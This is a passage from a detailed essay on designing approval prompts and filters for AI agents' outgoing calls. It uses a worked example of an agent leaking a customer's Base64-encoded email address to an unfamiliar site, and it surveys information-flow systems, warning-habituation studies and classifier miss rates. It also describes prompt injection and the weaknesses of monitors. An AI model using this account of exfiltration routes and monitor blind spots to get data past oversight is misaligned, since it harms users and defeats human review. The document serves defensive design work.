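4. Continue if they match. If they differ, stop and show a new prompt with the new destination and the data it would receive.

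The harness has to inspect the data again at step 4, because the first site may have copied the private value into the new address. Some redirects also require the client to resend the entire body of the original request, so a form or a file would go to the second site as well.

A second prompt is a logical extension of the rule that approval covers only the call the reviewer saw, but none of the URL studies tested one. Reviewers could also tire of these prompts, since logins and shortened links often cross from one domain to another. A harness could skip some of them by checking whether the exact URL is already public, as OpenAI does.

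The procedure also works only if the harness makes the web request itself. Suppose "fetch_page" runs on a remote MCP server. The harness sends the URL to that server, whose operator receives the customer's email address before the parcel site does. The server then follows any redirects, which the harness can't detect. In that case, the preview should name both recipients, for example "parcel-status.example, through fetch-tools.example", and state that the harness can't check for redirects.

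No design can prevent a site from passing data on after receiving it, so a reviewer who allows a call is trusting the recipient to decide where the data goes next.

### Recipients the user has never contacted

The harness often can't find out who owns a site, but it can check whether the user has sent data there before. Users can easily understand a label such as "You have never sent data to this address" without knowing how URLs work. The label would have appeared in the incident at Anthropic where an agent tried to publish a report on a public code-sharing site, if the user had never posted there.

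None of the studies described above tested such a label. The closest is a browser extension that warned people when they tried to type on a site outside the 10,000 most popular. *Effectiveness of a Phishing Warning in Field Settings* explains that the extension used this cutoff because more than 91% of phishing sites ranked below it. In a six-week field experiment, participants received a weekly link to a survey, and some of the links led to fake sites.

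In an early trial by Yang, Chen and colleagues, almost everyone who saw the warning on a fake site entered an incorrect password. Interviews afterwards revealed that only one person had done this on purpose, so it was rarely a precaution. Anyone testing a "never contacted" label should likewise ask people why they denied a call before crediting the label with the denial.

A site's popularity is also a poorer guide than the user's own history. An agent can send data to a stranger through a large hosting service, even if that service is one of the most popular sites in the world.

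Good evidence shows that familiarity affects people's decisions, sometimes for the worse. Dhamija and colleagues describe an experiment by Jagatic and others in which 72% of university students responded to a phishing email that seemed to come from a friend, compared with 16% when it came from an unknown address. A "new recipient" label would probably make reviewers more careful, but a "known recipient" label might make them less careful than they should be. Thompson and colleagues recommend active warnings about suspicious sites over passive signs of reassurance. By the same logic, the preview should label new recipients and leave familiar ones unlabeled.

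The label's value also depends on how the harness keeps its history:

- It should record accounts and addresses, not just domains. Otherwise one email to a colleague would make every other customer of the same mail provider look familiar.
- It should count only recipients to whom the user has knowingly sent something. If an agent's own page visits counted, a site could look familiar to the harness when the user had never heard of it.
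- It should start with the user's existing contacts and repositories. With an empty history, every recipient would be new during the first weeks, and people would learn to ignore the label.

Even with a good history, an agent researching on the web will often visit new sites. The harness can keep the label rare by showing it only when a call also carries private data.

### The destination line in the parcel lookup

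The earlier preview gave the site as "track.parcel-status.example". A more informative version would be:

```
The agent wants to open a web page.

Sends to:      parcel-status.example
               You have never sent data to this site.
               Owner unknown.
Data sent:     id = mara@example.org (decoded from Base64)
Your request:  Summarise this complaint and check on the parcel.

> Full address
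> Agent's explanation (written by the agent, not verified)

Allow        Deny
```

The word "track" now appears only in the full address, because the site's owner chose it and it makes the site look more official than the evidence supports. If parcel-status.example were a hosting service, "track" would identify the customer and would have to stay where it was.

Most people can't judge the domain unaided, so the prompt includes the two lines underneath. "Owner unknown" corrects the impression that a site with "parcel" in its name must belong to the carrier. If the user had saved the carrier's real website, the harness could show the carrier's name for calls to that site and leave out both lines.

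The new version would also appear for a genuine tracking service that the user had never used, and some reviewers would deny the call unnecessarily, as Dhamija's participants rejected the stockbroker's real site. A reviewer who remembers the address from the shop's delivery emails has a good reason to allow the call. One who doesn't can ask the shop which company is carrying the parcel before letting the agent send a customer's email address to an unfamiliar service.

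## Showing where the data came from

The preview now shows the reviewer that the parcel lookup sends mara@example.org to parcel-status.example, a site the user has never contacted. It doesn't show where the agent got the email address or the site. If the user had typed both into the request, allowing the call would usually be sensible.

Suppose instead that the complaint is record 4417 in the shop's customer database. Before proposing the call, the agent also opened a web page about tracking parcels. The agent copied the email address from the database and took the name of the site from the web page. The user chose neither the address nor the site, but a reviewer can't tell that from the decoded value and the destination.

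A record of provenance can answer two separate questions:

- Which source supplied the value? The email address came from the customer database.
- Which source prompted the action? It was probably the web page, because the user's request never mentioned parcel-status.example.

Knowing where a value came from helps the reviewer judge how private it is. An email address from a company's public contact page is harmless to send, but one from a customer database may not be. Knowing what prompted the action helps the reviewer judge whether the user wanted it.

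### How labels follow data

The usual way to record where data came from is information-flow control, in which software labels data by secrecy and trustworthiness and checks the labels before the data moves. Following the labels through a running program is called taint tracking.

The technique reached phones in 2010 with *TaintDroid*, which tracked several kinds of private data at once as Android apps used them. It slowed a processor-heavy test by only 14%, and it revealed potential misuse of private information in 20 of the 30 popular apps it monitored.

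An app consists of instructions with known inputs and outputs, so a tracker can follow a phone number from one variable to the next. A tracker can't follow data through a language model this way, because any word in the model's output might depend on any word in its input.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, adapted the technique to agents in a system called FIDES. It works in three steps:

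1. Label data on entry. When a tool returns a result, FIDES attaches a label to the whole result or to each field. The user's own message normally counts as trusted and public.
2. Carry the labels along. Anything the agent makes from labelled data gets a label that combines those of all the ingredients.
3. Check the labels at the outgoing call. FIDES compares the labels on the call and on each parameter with a policy, and runs the call only if it complies.

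A label can record secrecy as the set of people who may read a value, and trust as the set of people who may have written it. If the agent makes z from x and y, the labels combine like this:

readers(z) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)

writers(z) = writers(x) ∪ writers(y)

When an agent combines two pieces of data, only people allowed to read both may read the result, but anyone who could have influenced either piece could have influenced the result. For example, if the support and warehouse teams can read a complaint, and the warehouse team and the carrier can read a shipping record, only the warehouse team may read a summary of both.

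Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, describe two policies that they consider sufficient for most practical cases. "Permitted flow" requires that every recipient is allowed to read the data. "Trusted action" requires that only trusted sources influenced the decision to make the call and the parameters that matter.

In their system, a call that sends data out must pass at least one of the two checks. A user can tell the agent to send a confidential file to an outsider because the instruction comes from the user. A call prompted by the same instruction in an injected email would fail both.

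The parcel lookup fails both as well:

| Item | Who may read it | Who may have influenced it |
| --- | --- | --- |
| User's request | Anyone | The user |
| Complaint 4417 | The shop's support team | The customer |
| Web page about parcels | Anyone | The page's owner |
| Proposed call | The shop's support team | The user, the customer and the page's owner |

The operator of parcel-status.example is not on the support team, and two of the three parties that may have influenced the call are strangers. An "untrusted" label would be enough to block the call, but a preview has to name the parties to show the reviewer where the data came from.

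Encoding a value doesn't remove its label, because the harness attaches the label regardless of how the value is written. Labels can therefore show where a value came from even when the harness can't decode it.

### What four agent systems track

FIDES blocks any call that violates its policy, and its original design doesn't ask the user. With suitable policies, it stopped every prompt injection in AgentDojo, a set of test tasks for agents. Costa and colleagues found that it completed 8% more tasks than a basic agent subject to the same checks when both used GPT-4o, and 16% more when both used o1, a reasoning model.

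CaMeL, a system by Debenedetti and colleagues, goes further in controlling what can prompt an action. *An AI Agent Execution Environment to Safeguard User Data* (Stanley, Verma and colleagues, 2026) describes how an isolated model turns the user's request into a complete program before the agent reads anything else. A special interpreter then tracks data as the program runs. A web page can supply values to the program but can't add steps.

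An agent using CaMeL is less flexible because it can't change its plan in response to what it reads. Stanley and colleagues note that CaMeL reportedly completed none of the tasks in AgentDyn, a benchmark full of unexpected turns. CaMeL also follows a policy fixed in advance, so users can't set their own rules for who may receive which data.

Kolluri and colleagues built PRUDENTIA on top of FIDES and gave the user a larger role. The agent knows the labels and policies, so it can plan calls that comply with them. When a call would still break a policy, PRUDENTIA asks the user to approve it. It can also ask the user to endorse an untrusted document, which the agent may then treat as trusted. If an email contains a to-do list with ten items, one endorsement can replace ten approvals.

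To endorse an email, however, the user has to vouch that it contains no hidden instruction, a demanding judgement that an approval prompt at the outgoing call was supposed to spare them. Kolluri and colleagues deliberately left out the equivalent shortcut for secrecy, which would let a user declare a private document public. They reasoned that whether revealing private information is appropriate depends on the situation, so users should decide for each call.

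Stanley and colleagues' system, GAAP, focuses on where private data came from and where it may go. It treats the model, the tools and the user's prompt as potentially compromised, so it doesn't rely on trust labels. It gives each private item a name, such as "date of birth" or a file path. When an item is about to go to a recipient the user hasn't made a decision about, GAAP prompts the user for permission to share that item with that recipient, for example to email the contents of a named file to a particular address.

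This question is close to what the parcel prompt needs because it names both the source and the recipient. GAAP can display it only because someone has written a short description of each tool, specifying who receives its data. Without these descriptions, the question would be whether to share everything in the file system with everyone reachable by email, which no user could sensibly answer.

GAAP also logs what it has sent to each service. Suppose an agent gives an airline the user's passport number to check in for a flight, then tries to email the airline's confirmation to a friend. GAAP labels the confirmation as possibly containing the passport number and asks the user before sending it.

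| System | What it tracks | When it asks the user |
| --- | --- | --- |
| FIDES | Secrecy and trustworthiness of each value | It blocks the call instead |
| CaMeL | Data moving through a program written in advance | Not by default |
| PRUDENTIA | The same labels as FIDES | When a call breaks a policy, or to endorse untrusted data |
| GAAP | The name of each private item, and which services have already received it | When an item would go to a recipient the user hasn't ruled on |

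Stanley and colleagues tried seven attacks on each of 20 tasks, and GAAP prevented all the leaks. It completed up to 10% fewer tasks than an unprotected agent and averaged 188 seconds per task, compared with 28. GAAP's guarantee covers only data privacy, so an injected instruction could still make the agent take unwanted actions that don't disclose data.

All these systems depend on labeling data correctly when it enters. GAAP, for example, doesn't protect anything typed directly into the prompt, so users need to leave private details out and refer to them by name.

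### When everything gets a label

Once a model has read a secret, everything it writes may depend on it. If the agent reads complaint 4417 and then searches for the weather in Leeds, the search query inherits the complaint's label. A preview that relied on the label alone would warn that the query might contain customer data. After an hour of work, the warning could list every document the agent had opened.

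This over-labelling is safe in that the system never loses track of a secret, but it makes the labels useless to a reviewer because nearly every call has the same ones. Labels can spread quickly in *Flowsh* (2026), a command shell for agents. It gives each file a single label, so one confidential line makes a whole report confidential. Each command also combines the labels of all the inputs that may have influenced its output.

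FIDES limits the problem by keeping some data away from the model. When a tool result would add restrictions, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, such as "#read_emails_0". The model can then call a tool to send "#read_emails_0" to a colleague without reading the emails. The decision to send them remains trusted, and the harness can identify exactly which tool result will leave, so a preview could name the source with certainty.

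Many tasks require a model to read the text, though. To summarize emails, for example, FIDES passes the variable that holds them to a separate model with no tools, and puts the answer in a new variable with its own label. The main model still hasn't read the emails, so its later calls don't inherit their restrictions.

FIDES can also restrict the form of the answer. A yes-or-no answer carries one bit, so a policy may let the main model read it even if the document it came from is untrusted. The policy should count these answers, because many one-bit answers can together reveal a secret.

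Costa and colleagues mention another approach, by Siddiqui and colleagues, which identifies the messages that influenced a model's response and regenerates the response from only those messages. The new response needs only those messages' labels. In the Leeds example, the search query would be much the same without the complaint, so it may not need the complaint's label.

These measures may be enough for some kinds of work. None of the 20 tasks in GAAP's own test suite failed because of over-labelling. But those tasks used tools with well-defined inputs, and data is much harder to track precisely through a coding agent that runs arbitrary commands.

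Labels can also miss information. FIDES tracks data that the agent copies into a call, but not what someone could infer from which calls it makes. If an agent opens one page when a customer is owed a refund and another when they aren't, the choice of page reveals the answer even though neither address contains it.

*SPA* (2026), a system that keeps labels from one user request to the next, covers this case by applying a decision's label to every step that depends on that decision. Both page requests would inherit the restrictions on the customer's record. This adds more labels, which makes over-labelling worse.

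### Searching for the value instead

String matching takes much less work. The harness keeps the text that tools return and searches it for each value the agent is about to send. In the parcel lookup, it would decode the "id" field, search for mara@example.org and find it in complaint 4417. This result is more specific than a label that lists everything the agent has read, and the method requires no changes to the model or its tools.

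String matching fails when the agent rewrites the information. Suppose a customer says they missed a delivery because they were in hospital for chemotherapy, and the agent tells the carrier that "the recipient is being treated for cancer". The two sentences may share no distinctive words, but the second discloses the most private fact in the first. Translations, totals and summaries cause the same problem.

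It can also find too many matches, because a quantity of "2" or the word "London" may appear in dozens of documents. The harness can ignore short and common values unless they come from a field known to be private, such as a PIN.

The two methods work best together. The preview can name the document if the harness finds an exact match, and otherwise use the labels to list the private sources the agent had read. The preview should never present the lack of a match as evidence that the data is harmless.

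### Why an outside influence may be harmless

A warning shown to the reviewer whenever outside content shaped a call would often be wrong. *Influence Is Not Authority* (Ahad, Hossain and colleagues, August 2026) gives the example of a user who asks an agent to send money to Alice without including her account number. The agent has to look it up, so a tool's output must influence the transfer even though the user chose the recipient.

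Ahad and colleagues built 24 pairs of cases in which the agent took the same authorised action with the same values. The only difference was whether one necessary value came from the user or from a legitimate tool. They then scored each action with a measure based on an existing guardrail. It removes one source at a time to estimate how much each supports the action, then compares the user's request with the outside content:

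score = support from the user − support from outside content

The lower the score, the more an action looks like an attack. Moving the value from the user to the tool lowered the score in all 24 pairs, with either Llama or Gemma as the scorer. With Llama, the score fell by 1.18 on average, because support from the user fell by 0.43 and support from the tool rose by 0.75. Changing the action to an unauthorised one, such as paying Mallory instead of Alice, lowered the score by only another 0.53.

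Unauthorised actions scored lower on average, but no threshold separated them well from authorised ones. The strictest threshold that flagged no authorised action caught 25% of the unauthorised ones with Llama and 37.5% with Gemma.

The pairs were artificial, so they don't show how often this happens in practice. Ahad and colleagues also examined 29 consequential decisions in ordinary test tasks with no attack. The user's request was the main influence in 75% of cases where the user had supplied the necessary value, compared with 17% where the agent had to look it up.

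*From Agent Traces to Trust* (Wang, Zhang and colleagues, 2026), a survey of provenance in agents, similarly distinguishes what influenced a decision from what justifies it. For instance, a false note in an agent's memory can cause an action without justifying it.

*PROVISO* (Yan, Zhang and colleagues, 2026) proposes a more useful test, based on what the outside source contributed. The user, or whoever deployed the agent, must authorise the type of action and its target, but other details may come from outside. If a user asks an agent to pay an invoice to account B, the amount can come from the invoice, but an instruction in the invoice to pay account C doesn't count as authorisation.

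The parcel lookup is harder to classify. The user asked the agent to check on the parcel but didn't name a site, so the agent had to find one. If the site's address came from the shop's shipping record, it would resemble Alice's account number, which the agent was supposed to look up. If it came from an unknown web page, it would be closer to account C. The reviewer can tell these cases apart only if the preview shows where the address came from.

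### Whether people use information about sources

Hossain and colleagues ran the closest test of this with people. The best version of their prompt included a sentence linking the data to its source, such as "The attachment was built from raw invoice rows." Participants who saw that version answered 81.7% of comprehension questions correctly, compared with 76.7% for those who saw the same facts in a log and 57.1% for those who saw only a short description.

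The log appeared with the user's original instructions, so the experiment can't isolate the benefit of showing sources. When a violation depended on data passing through several steps, people approved 7 of 30 malicious requests whether they saw the linking sentence or the plain log.

*Bolt-on, Verifiable Provenance for LLM-Powered Data Processing* (2026) describes a study in which eight people checked a model's answers against passages from the original documents. They found long passages hard to interpret, even when the passages contained nothing unnecessary. One participant complained that a passage looked like a search result and didn't explain the answer. A reviewer with a tool call waiting has less time than someone checking an answer, so a preview should probably give a short source name and show the passage only on request.

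Even if people understand where data came from, they may not notice that the task doesn't need it. Wu, Yang and colleagues (2025), in *Towards Automating Data Access Permissions in AI Agents*, recruited 205 people to train an imaginary personal assistant. For each scenario, participants first chose the data they thought the assistant would need and then decided what it could share. They could allow or refuse sharing, either once or always.

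Each participant answered 20 permission questions, 5 of which included data that the task didn't require. Wu and colleagues had asked participants about privacy beforehand to make them more cautious, and every question warned that the assistant might collect unnecessary data. Even so, 97% of participants shared unnecessary data at least once.

| Was the data necessary? | Did the participant think so? | Shared |
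| --- | --- | --- |
| Yes | Yes | 89% |
| Yes | No | 67% |
| No | Yes | 78% |
| No | No | 38% |

People shared more than a third of the data they had correctly judged unnecessary. Seeing the assistant ask for it may have changed their minds. Wu and colleagues suggest that many users tend to believe an agent even when it is wrong.

Participants were more careful with data that was obviously sensitive. They withheld Social Security numbers about 46% of the time, even though the tasks often needed them. They shared more than necessary in 89% of cases involving a workspace name, which sounds harmless but has no obvious purpose.

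The scenarios were hypothetical, the researchers decided which data each tool needed, and the questions didn't test source labels. A label such as "from the customer database" could make an ordinary-looking value seem more sensitive, but it wouldn't show whether the tool needed the value. To judge that, the reviewer would have to know the job or get a description of the tool's requirements from the harness.

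Wu and colleagues also trained a model to predict participants' choices. Its predictions were right 85.1% of the time overall, and 94.4% of the time when limited to those with the highest confidence. Without any record of a person's earlier decisions, accuracy was 66.9%.

Accuracy here means agreement with the participant. A model that learned from someone who overshares would score well by oversharing on their behalf, so the prediction is a better guide to a person's habits than to whether a disclosure is safe.

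### Why products don't show trust labels

Wang and colleagues found eight research papers that proposed letting users see or assign trust labels, but none of the 21 production systems in their survey offered this. They attribute this to the effort involved and, more importantly, to users' understanding of data, which rarely includes sets of permitted readers and rules for combining those sets.

This explanation is plausible, but Wang and colleagues did not test it on users. It also applies mainly to asking people to assign labels, which is much more work than reading them. Over-labelling may be another obstacle, since putting "may contain private data" on every call would only annoy users.

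In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) reviewed 21 proposed permission systems. In those with security labels, users often labelled their own request but not external data or tools. The harness or its developers have to label those.

Wang and colleagues suggest first distinguishing only trusted from untrusted sources, then adding detail as users gain experience. For an approval prompt, naming the source may be simpler still. Reviewers can understand "from a web page" without learning any labels, and they can decide how much to trust the page. An "untrusted" tag alone would also apply to the complaint that the user asked the agent to read.

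### Source labels in the parcel lookup

With sources added, the preview might look like this:

```
The agent wants to open a web page.

Sends to:      parcel-status.example
               You have never sent data to this site.
               Owner unknown.
               Site named by: web page at parcel-help.example
Data sent:     id = mara@example.org (decoded from Base64)
               Found in: customer database, complaint 4417
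Your request:  Summarise this complaint and check on the parcel.

> Full address
> What the agent read before this call (2 sources)
> Agent's explanation (written by the agent, not verified)

Allow        Deny
```

Both new lines come from string matching. The harness searched the user's request for the site's address, didn't find it, and then found it on the web page. The preview uses "Site named by" instead of "Prompted by" because the harness can't prove that the page caused the call. If the user had typed the address, the line would read "You gave this address". If it had come from the shop's own shipping record, the preview would name that record, and the reviewer would have much less reason to worry.

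The harness should write the source descriptions itself, using the address it connected to or the database it queried. A stranger can choose the title of a web page or the name of an attached file, so a title such as "Official carrier instructions" shouldn't appear as though the harness had verified it.

If the harness can't decode the value, string matching won't work, but the labels still help:

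```
Data sent:     id = q7Xk2mVb9TzR4wLs8NcHfA
               Could not decode. The agent wrote this after reading:
               customer database, complaint 4417
```

The preview lists the complaint because it is private and leaves out the web page because anyone can read it. If the agent had read many private sources, the preview could show the most sensitive one and how many others there were.

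Labels also help the harness recognise when a value is going back unchanged to the server that issued it. This needs no warning. For example, if an agent passes a shop's basket identifier back through a variable, the harness can confirm that the model didn't alter it.

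## Deciding when to interrupt the reviewer

A preview that shows the destination, the data and its sources takes time to read. Participants in Hossain and colleagues' study spent about half a minute on the fullest version of the preview, so the harness has to choose which calls are worth a prompt.

### How quickly attention falls

People can habituate to prompts after seeing only a few. In *Harder to Ignore?*, Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues (2014) had online workers click "Yes" on as many pop-up dialogs as they could in a limited time. After 1, 3 or 20 dialogs, or 150 seconds of them, the text changed to tell people to click "No", which would end the task early. The researchers counted how many people clicked "No" the first time the new text appeared.

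Busse, Fahl and colleagues (2019), in *Replication*, repeated part of the experiment and listed both sets of results:

| Dialogs before the change | Clicked "No" in 2014 | Clicked "No" in the repeat | Median time on the last ordinary dialog in 2014 |
| --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 1 | 47% (50 of 106) | 28% (28 of 99) | 10 seconds |
| 3 | 40% (43 of 107) | 22% (23 of 104) | 3.4 seconds |
| 20 | 21% (24 of 114) | 15% (14 of 94) | 1.2 seconds |

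By the twentieth dialog, people clicked after about a second, too fast to read anything. But more than half missed the change after a single dialog, so habituation explains only part of the problem. The task also rewarded speed, as a busy working day does.

In another version, people had to move the cursor across the text before they could click "Yes". In 2014, this kept the success rate between 55% and 58% however many dialogs people had seen, and Bravo-Lillo and colleagues concluded that it appeared resilient to habituation. In the repeat study, the rate fell from 55% after one dialog to 37% after twenty, which was still better than with the plain dialog.

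Nobody in those experiments lost anything by clicking the wrong button. Busse and colleagues therefore ran a larger experiment with 1,236 people, in which some could build up a bonus of 50 cents and lost all of it if they opened a message from an unknown signer. The bonus reduced the share of wrong choices by 12 to 14 percentage points. Seeing 20 safe dialogs first, instead of one, raised that share by 16 points, an effect at least as large as the bonus's.

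Brain imaging shows the same decline before it appears in behaviour. *How Polymorphic Warnings Reduce Habituation in the Brain* (Anderson, Kirwan and colleagues, 2015) found that activity in the brain's visual processing centres dropped dramatically on only the second exposure to a warning, and kept dropping after that. "Polymorphic" warnings, which change their appearance each time, held attention better.

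Vance, Jenkins and colleagues (2018) followed the effect over a working week in *Tuning Out Security Warnings*. Each day they scanned 15 people while showing them 40 different warnings, four times each. Eye tracking showed that the average number of fixations (points where the eye rests) fell from 9.1 on the first day to 7.4 on the fifth. Attention partly recovered overnight, but not enough to cancel the decline.

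Their second experiment measured what people did. For 15 weekdays, 102 students downloaded and ranked three apps a day on their own phones, using an app store the researchers had secretly built. A warning before each download listed what the app could do. The researchers told participants to refuse any app with one of four risky permissions, such as selling the user's browsing data, and used a quiz to check that they knew all four.

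At the start, participants refused 87% of the risky apps. After three weeks, those who always saw the same design refused 55%, and those who saw changing designs refused 76%.

Participants saw an average of only 4.7 warnings a day, whereas Anthropic estimates that its prompts required dozens or hundreds of decisions from developers. Reducing prompts to a handful a day may therefore not be enough to keep people careful. Another possible explanation is that some participants noticed the risky permission and stopped believing that it mattered, because more than a third of the warnings were for risky apps and nothing bad visibly happened to people who installed one.

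Prompts unrelated to security also reduce the attention people pay to security warnings. *The Fog of Warnings* reports an online experiment in which habituation to a frequent, harmless notification carried over to a security warning that people saw only once. The effect was stronger the more alike the two looked, and the researchers ruled out fatigue as the cause. If a harness uses the same dialog for "Run the tests?" and "Send this customer's email address?", people learn from the first to ignore the second.

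### What phones taught designers about asking

Phone makers had to decide when to ask users for permission long before AI agents existed. For *Android Permissions Remystified* (2015), Wijesekera, Baokar and colleagues gave 36 people modified Android phones for a week and logged 27 million requests by apps for protected resources. Earlier researchers had recommended asking users for 12 of the permissions, such as those for location, text messages and browser history, when an app tries to use them.

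Prompting the user on every request would have been unworkable, because apps requested those 12 permissions 11,598 times per user per day. Even if the phone had asked only when a request exposed sensitive data or sent a message, it would have shown 5,111 prompts a day, or one every 17 seconds.

Asking only the first time, as iPhones did, has a different weakness, because one approval then covers later requests that the user may not have agreed to. About three quarters of the logged requests came while the user had no sign that the app was running. Someone who shares their location with an app to find a restaurant hasn't necessarily agreed to let it track them overnight. Likewise, a user who lets an agent look up one parcel number on a website hasn't agreed to let it send that site an email address.

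At the end of the week, participants looked at screenshots of what they had been doing when apps made some of these requests. They would have blocked 149 of the 423 requests, or 35%. In just over half of those cases, they thought the app didn't need the data to function. People's objections followed a pattern, which suggested to Wijesekera and colleagues that software could learn when to ask.

*The Feasibility of Dynamically Granted Permissions* (2017) describes a model in which the system grants a request if it can determine that the data flow is appropriate, refuses if it can determine that the flow is inappropriate, and asks the user only if it can't determine either.

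Google later tested a similar idea on websites' requests to send notifications. *"Shhh...be quiet!" Reducing the Unwanted Interruptions of Notification Permission Prompts on Chrome* covers more than 40 million users and 100 million prompts. Chrome made the prompt less intrusive, using an adaptive rule and a list of sites known for interrupting people. Users took up to 30% fewer unnecessary actions on prompts, while the rate at which they granted permission changed by less than 5%. The stakes were low, however, because users who miss a notification prompt can turn notifications on later, whereas they can't take back a leaked email address.

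### The arithmetic of rare leaks

Even an attentive reviewer will mostly deny the wrong calls if leaks are rare. With the error rates from Yan's study and one harmful prompt in 1,000, only about one denial in a hundred is correct. In general, if p is the share of prompts that are harmful, d is the share of harmful calls the reviewer denies, and f is the false alarm rate:

share of denials that stop a leak = p·d / (p·d + (1 − p)·f)

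In Yan's study, d was 59.6% and f was 5.9% for people who saw a prompt for every action. A clearer preview would improve both, but with p at 1 in 1,000 it can't do much. If it reduced the false alarm rate from 5.9% to 1%, the share of correct denials would rise only to 5.6%. For half the denials to be correct, p would have to be:

p = f / (d + f) = 0.059 / 0.655 = 0.09

That is about one harmful call in every 11 prompts, or 90 times the rate among all the agent's calls. Only a filter that removes most harmless calls before anyone sees them can reach that rate. The figure of 1 in 1,000 is only an illustration. The true rate is probably lower for a user who isn't under attack, which makes filtering more important.

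People who see too many prompts also find ways to stop them, so a product that asks about every action may leave many users seeing no prompts at all. According to Anthropic, 25% of interactive Claude Code sessions in June 2026 began in a mode that skips permission prompts. Nearly half of the active users of its command-line version had written a rule letting some shell commands run without asking.

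### Safe Url and addresses that are already public

OpenAI's Safe Url applies the filter to web addresses. An independent crawler scans public pages, as a search engine does, and records the addresses it finds, without access to users' conversations or accounts. When an agent is about to open an address on its own, the harness checks whether the crawler has recorded exactly that address.

If a web address has already been published independently of the conversation, ChatGPT loads the page without a prompt, because the address is very unlikely to contain private data from that conversation. Otherwise, ChatGPT either tells the agent to try another website or warns the user before opening anything.

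OpenAI rejected a list of trusted websites as a complete solution for two reasons. Many reputable sites redirect visitors elsewhere, so checking the first domain doesn't establish where the request ends up. A strict list would also produce constant false alarms, because people use far more of the web than any list covers, and people who get many false alarms learn to click through the prompts.

Matching the exact address largely avoids both problems. Redirects matter less because an address that contains nothing from the conversation gives the first site nothing private to pass on. An obscure blog loads as easily as a famous newspaper if the crawler has seen the page. The check also works on large hosting services, where a trusted domain may contain thousands of strangers' pages.

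The warning is titled "Check this link is safe". The user reads that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with a third-party site, sees the address, and can copy or open it. The user now knows why the prompt appeared, but still can't tell what the data is if it's encoded.

OpenAI's help page *ChatGPT generated links* extends the idea to links that users click themselves. If someone asks where to buy a car, ChatGPT might offer a link ending in "car_search/London", and clicking it would reveal to the car site where they live. Some website owners ask OpenAI not to catalogue their sites, and ChatGPT asks users to confirm every link to those sites. People who use such a site often will see the warning mostly on harmless links and will probably get used to it.

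OpenAI's paper *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents* gives the technical details, and Embrace The Red summarises it in *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*. The security researcher who writes the blog reported this kind of leak to OpenAI in early 2023 and understands that an address the user types into the chat also counts as safe for that session. The researcher calls the crawler check a significant improvement, but small leaks remain possible, according to both the blog and the paper.

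Another weakness is that the check protects only the features it has been added to. The blog's author found that OpenAI's first version, from December 2023, was missing from the company's Mac and iPhone apps, and warns that a developer who doesn't know about the check may leave it out of a new feature. OpenAI says the check now also covers navigation and bookmarks in Atlas, its browser, and searches and navigation in Deep Research, its research agent.

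OpenAI promises only that the agent won't quietly leak a user's data through the web address of a page it loads. A page that loads without a warning may still contain false information or hidden instructions, or try to trick the user. Email bodies, uploaded files and messages to chat channels have no public web address to check, so they need a different filter.

### Prompting at the edge of a sandbox

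In a sandbox, the operating system limits what a program can reach, for example to one folder with no network access. An agent can edit files and run tests there without asking for permission. A prompt appears only when a command needs something outside the sandbox.

Sandboxing has a great advantage over reading commands for preventing exfiltration, because it doesn't depend on understanding what a command does. Weng's analyser marked 87% of normal commands as uninspectable, but a script that can't open a network connection can't send data out, whatever is encoded inside it.

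In OpenAI's ChatGPT Canvas and ChatGPT Apps, the agent builds small working programs that run in a sandbox. The sandbox asks the user for consent when it detects unexpected communication.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes sandboxing as safe but high-maintenance, because someone has to configure each new capability, and any task that needs the network or the rest of the computer breaks the isolation. An agent that edits code offline might run for hours without a prompt, but one that installs packages, reads documentation and pushes its work would constantly reach the sandbox's boundary.

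Boundary prompts also tend to cover only the connection, but spotting a leak requires knowing what is being sent and to which account. The sandbox can detect that a program is trying to connect to a code-hosting site, but encryption normally hides what the program will send. If the user allows the site, later uploads to it may pass without a prompt, including one to a stranger's public repository. The harness can show a more precise prompt if it sends the data itself through a narrow tool, because it then has the contents and the account before anything is sent.

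A sandbox around the shell doesn't cover calls to remote MCP servers. The harness's own client sends those calls, so the harness has to treat each one as data leaving.

### How auto mode routes a call

Claude Code's auto mode doesn't send every call to its classifier. It sorts calls into three tiers:

1. Tools that can't change anything, such as reading and searching files, run immediately. So do calls that match the user's own narrow rules. Auto mode sets aside rules broad enough to allow arbitrary code, since they would let the riskiest commands skip the classifier.
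2. Edits to files inside the project also run immediately, because the user can review and undo them later.
3. The classifier checks everything else, including shell commands, web requests and calls to outside tools.

The classifier works in two stages. A fast filter answers yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags a call, the model examines the same call again with step-by-step reasoning. Anthropic tested both stages on real calls by its employees and on 1,000 synthetic attempts at exfiltration, many of them disguised:

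| | Harmless calls blocked | Exfiltration missed |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Fast filter alone | 8.5% | 1.8% |
| Both stages | 0.4% | 5.7% |

The extra reasoning removed about 95% of the false alarms and let roughly three times as many leaks through. In a much smaller set of 52 real actions where the agent overstepped its instructions, the two stages together missed 17%. In these misses, the classifier usually detected the danger but wrongly treated the action as one the user had agreed to. For example, a user who says "clean up the PR" (pull request) hasn't clearly agreed to let the agent overwrite its history.

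The classifier sees the user's messages and the agent's calls, but not the agent's explanations or the results that tools return. This prevents the agent from arguing for an action and keeps instructions hidden in tool results from reaching the classifier. But it also removes the information about where data came from, which the parcel preview relies on. In the parcel lookup, the classifier would not see the complaint, so it couldn't tell that the email address came from there.

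Auto mode would probably block the call anyway. By default, it trusts only the code repository the user is working in, and one of its rules covers sending data to a service the user never specified. The user asked about a parcel but never mentioned parcel-status.example.

A block in Claude Code doesn't normally interrupt the user. The agent receives the refusal with a reason and looks for a safer way to continue, so a false alarm usually leads to just one retry. The user gets control back only after repeated blocks. If nobody is there to ask, as in an automated run, Claude Code stops. At Gusto, a payroll company, about 10% of sessions included at least one block, and fewer would have had enough blocks to return control to the user.

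In auto mode, Anthropic does not let users approve exfiltration, a rule it calls a hard denial. To see the advantage of blocking over asking, suppose an agent makes 100,000 calls, 100 of which would leak data. At the error rates Anthropic measured, the classifier would flag 94 of the leaks and about 400 harmless calls.

| What happens to the flagged calls | Leaks stopped | Harmless calls stopped |
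| --- | --- | --- |
| The harness blocks them all | 94 | 400 |
| A reviewer with the error rates from Yan's study decides | 56 | 24 |

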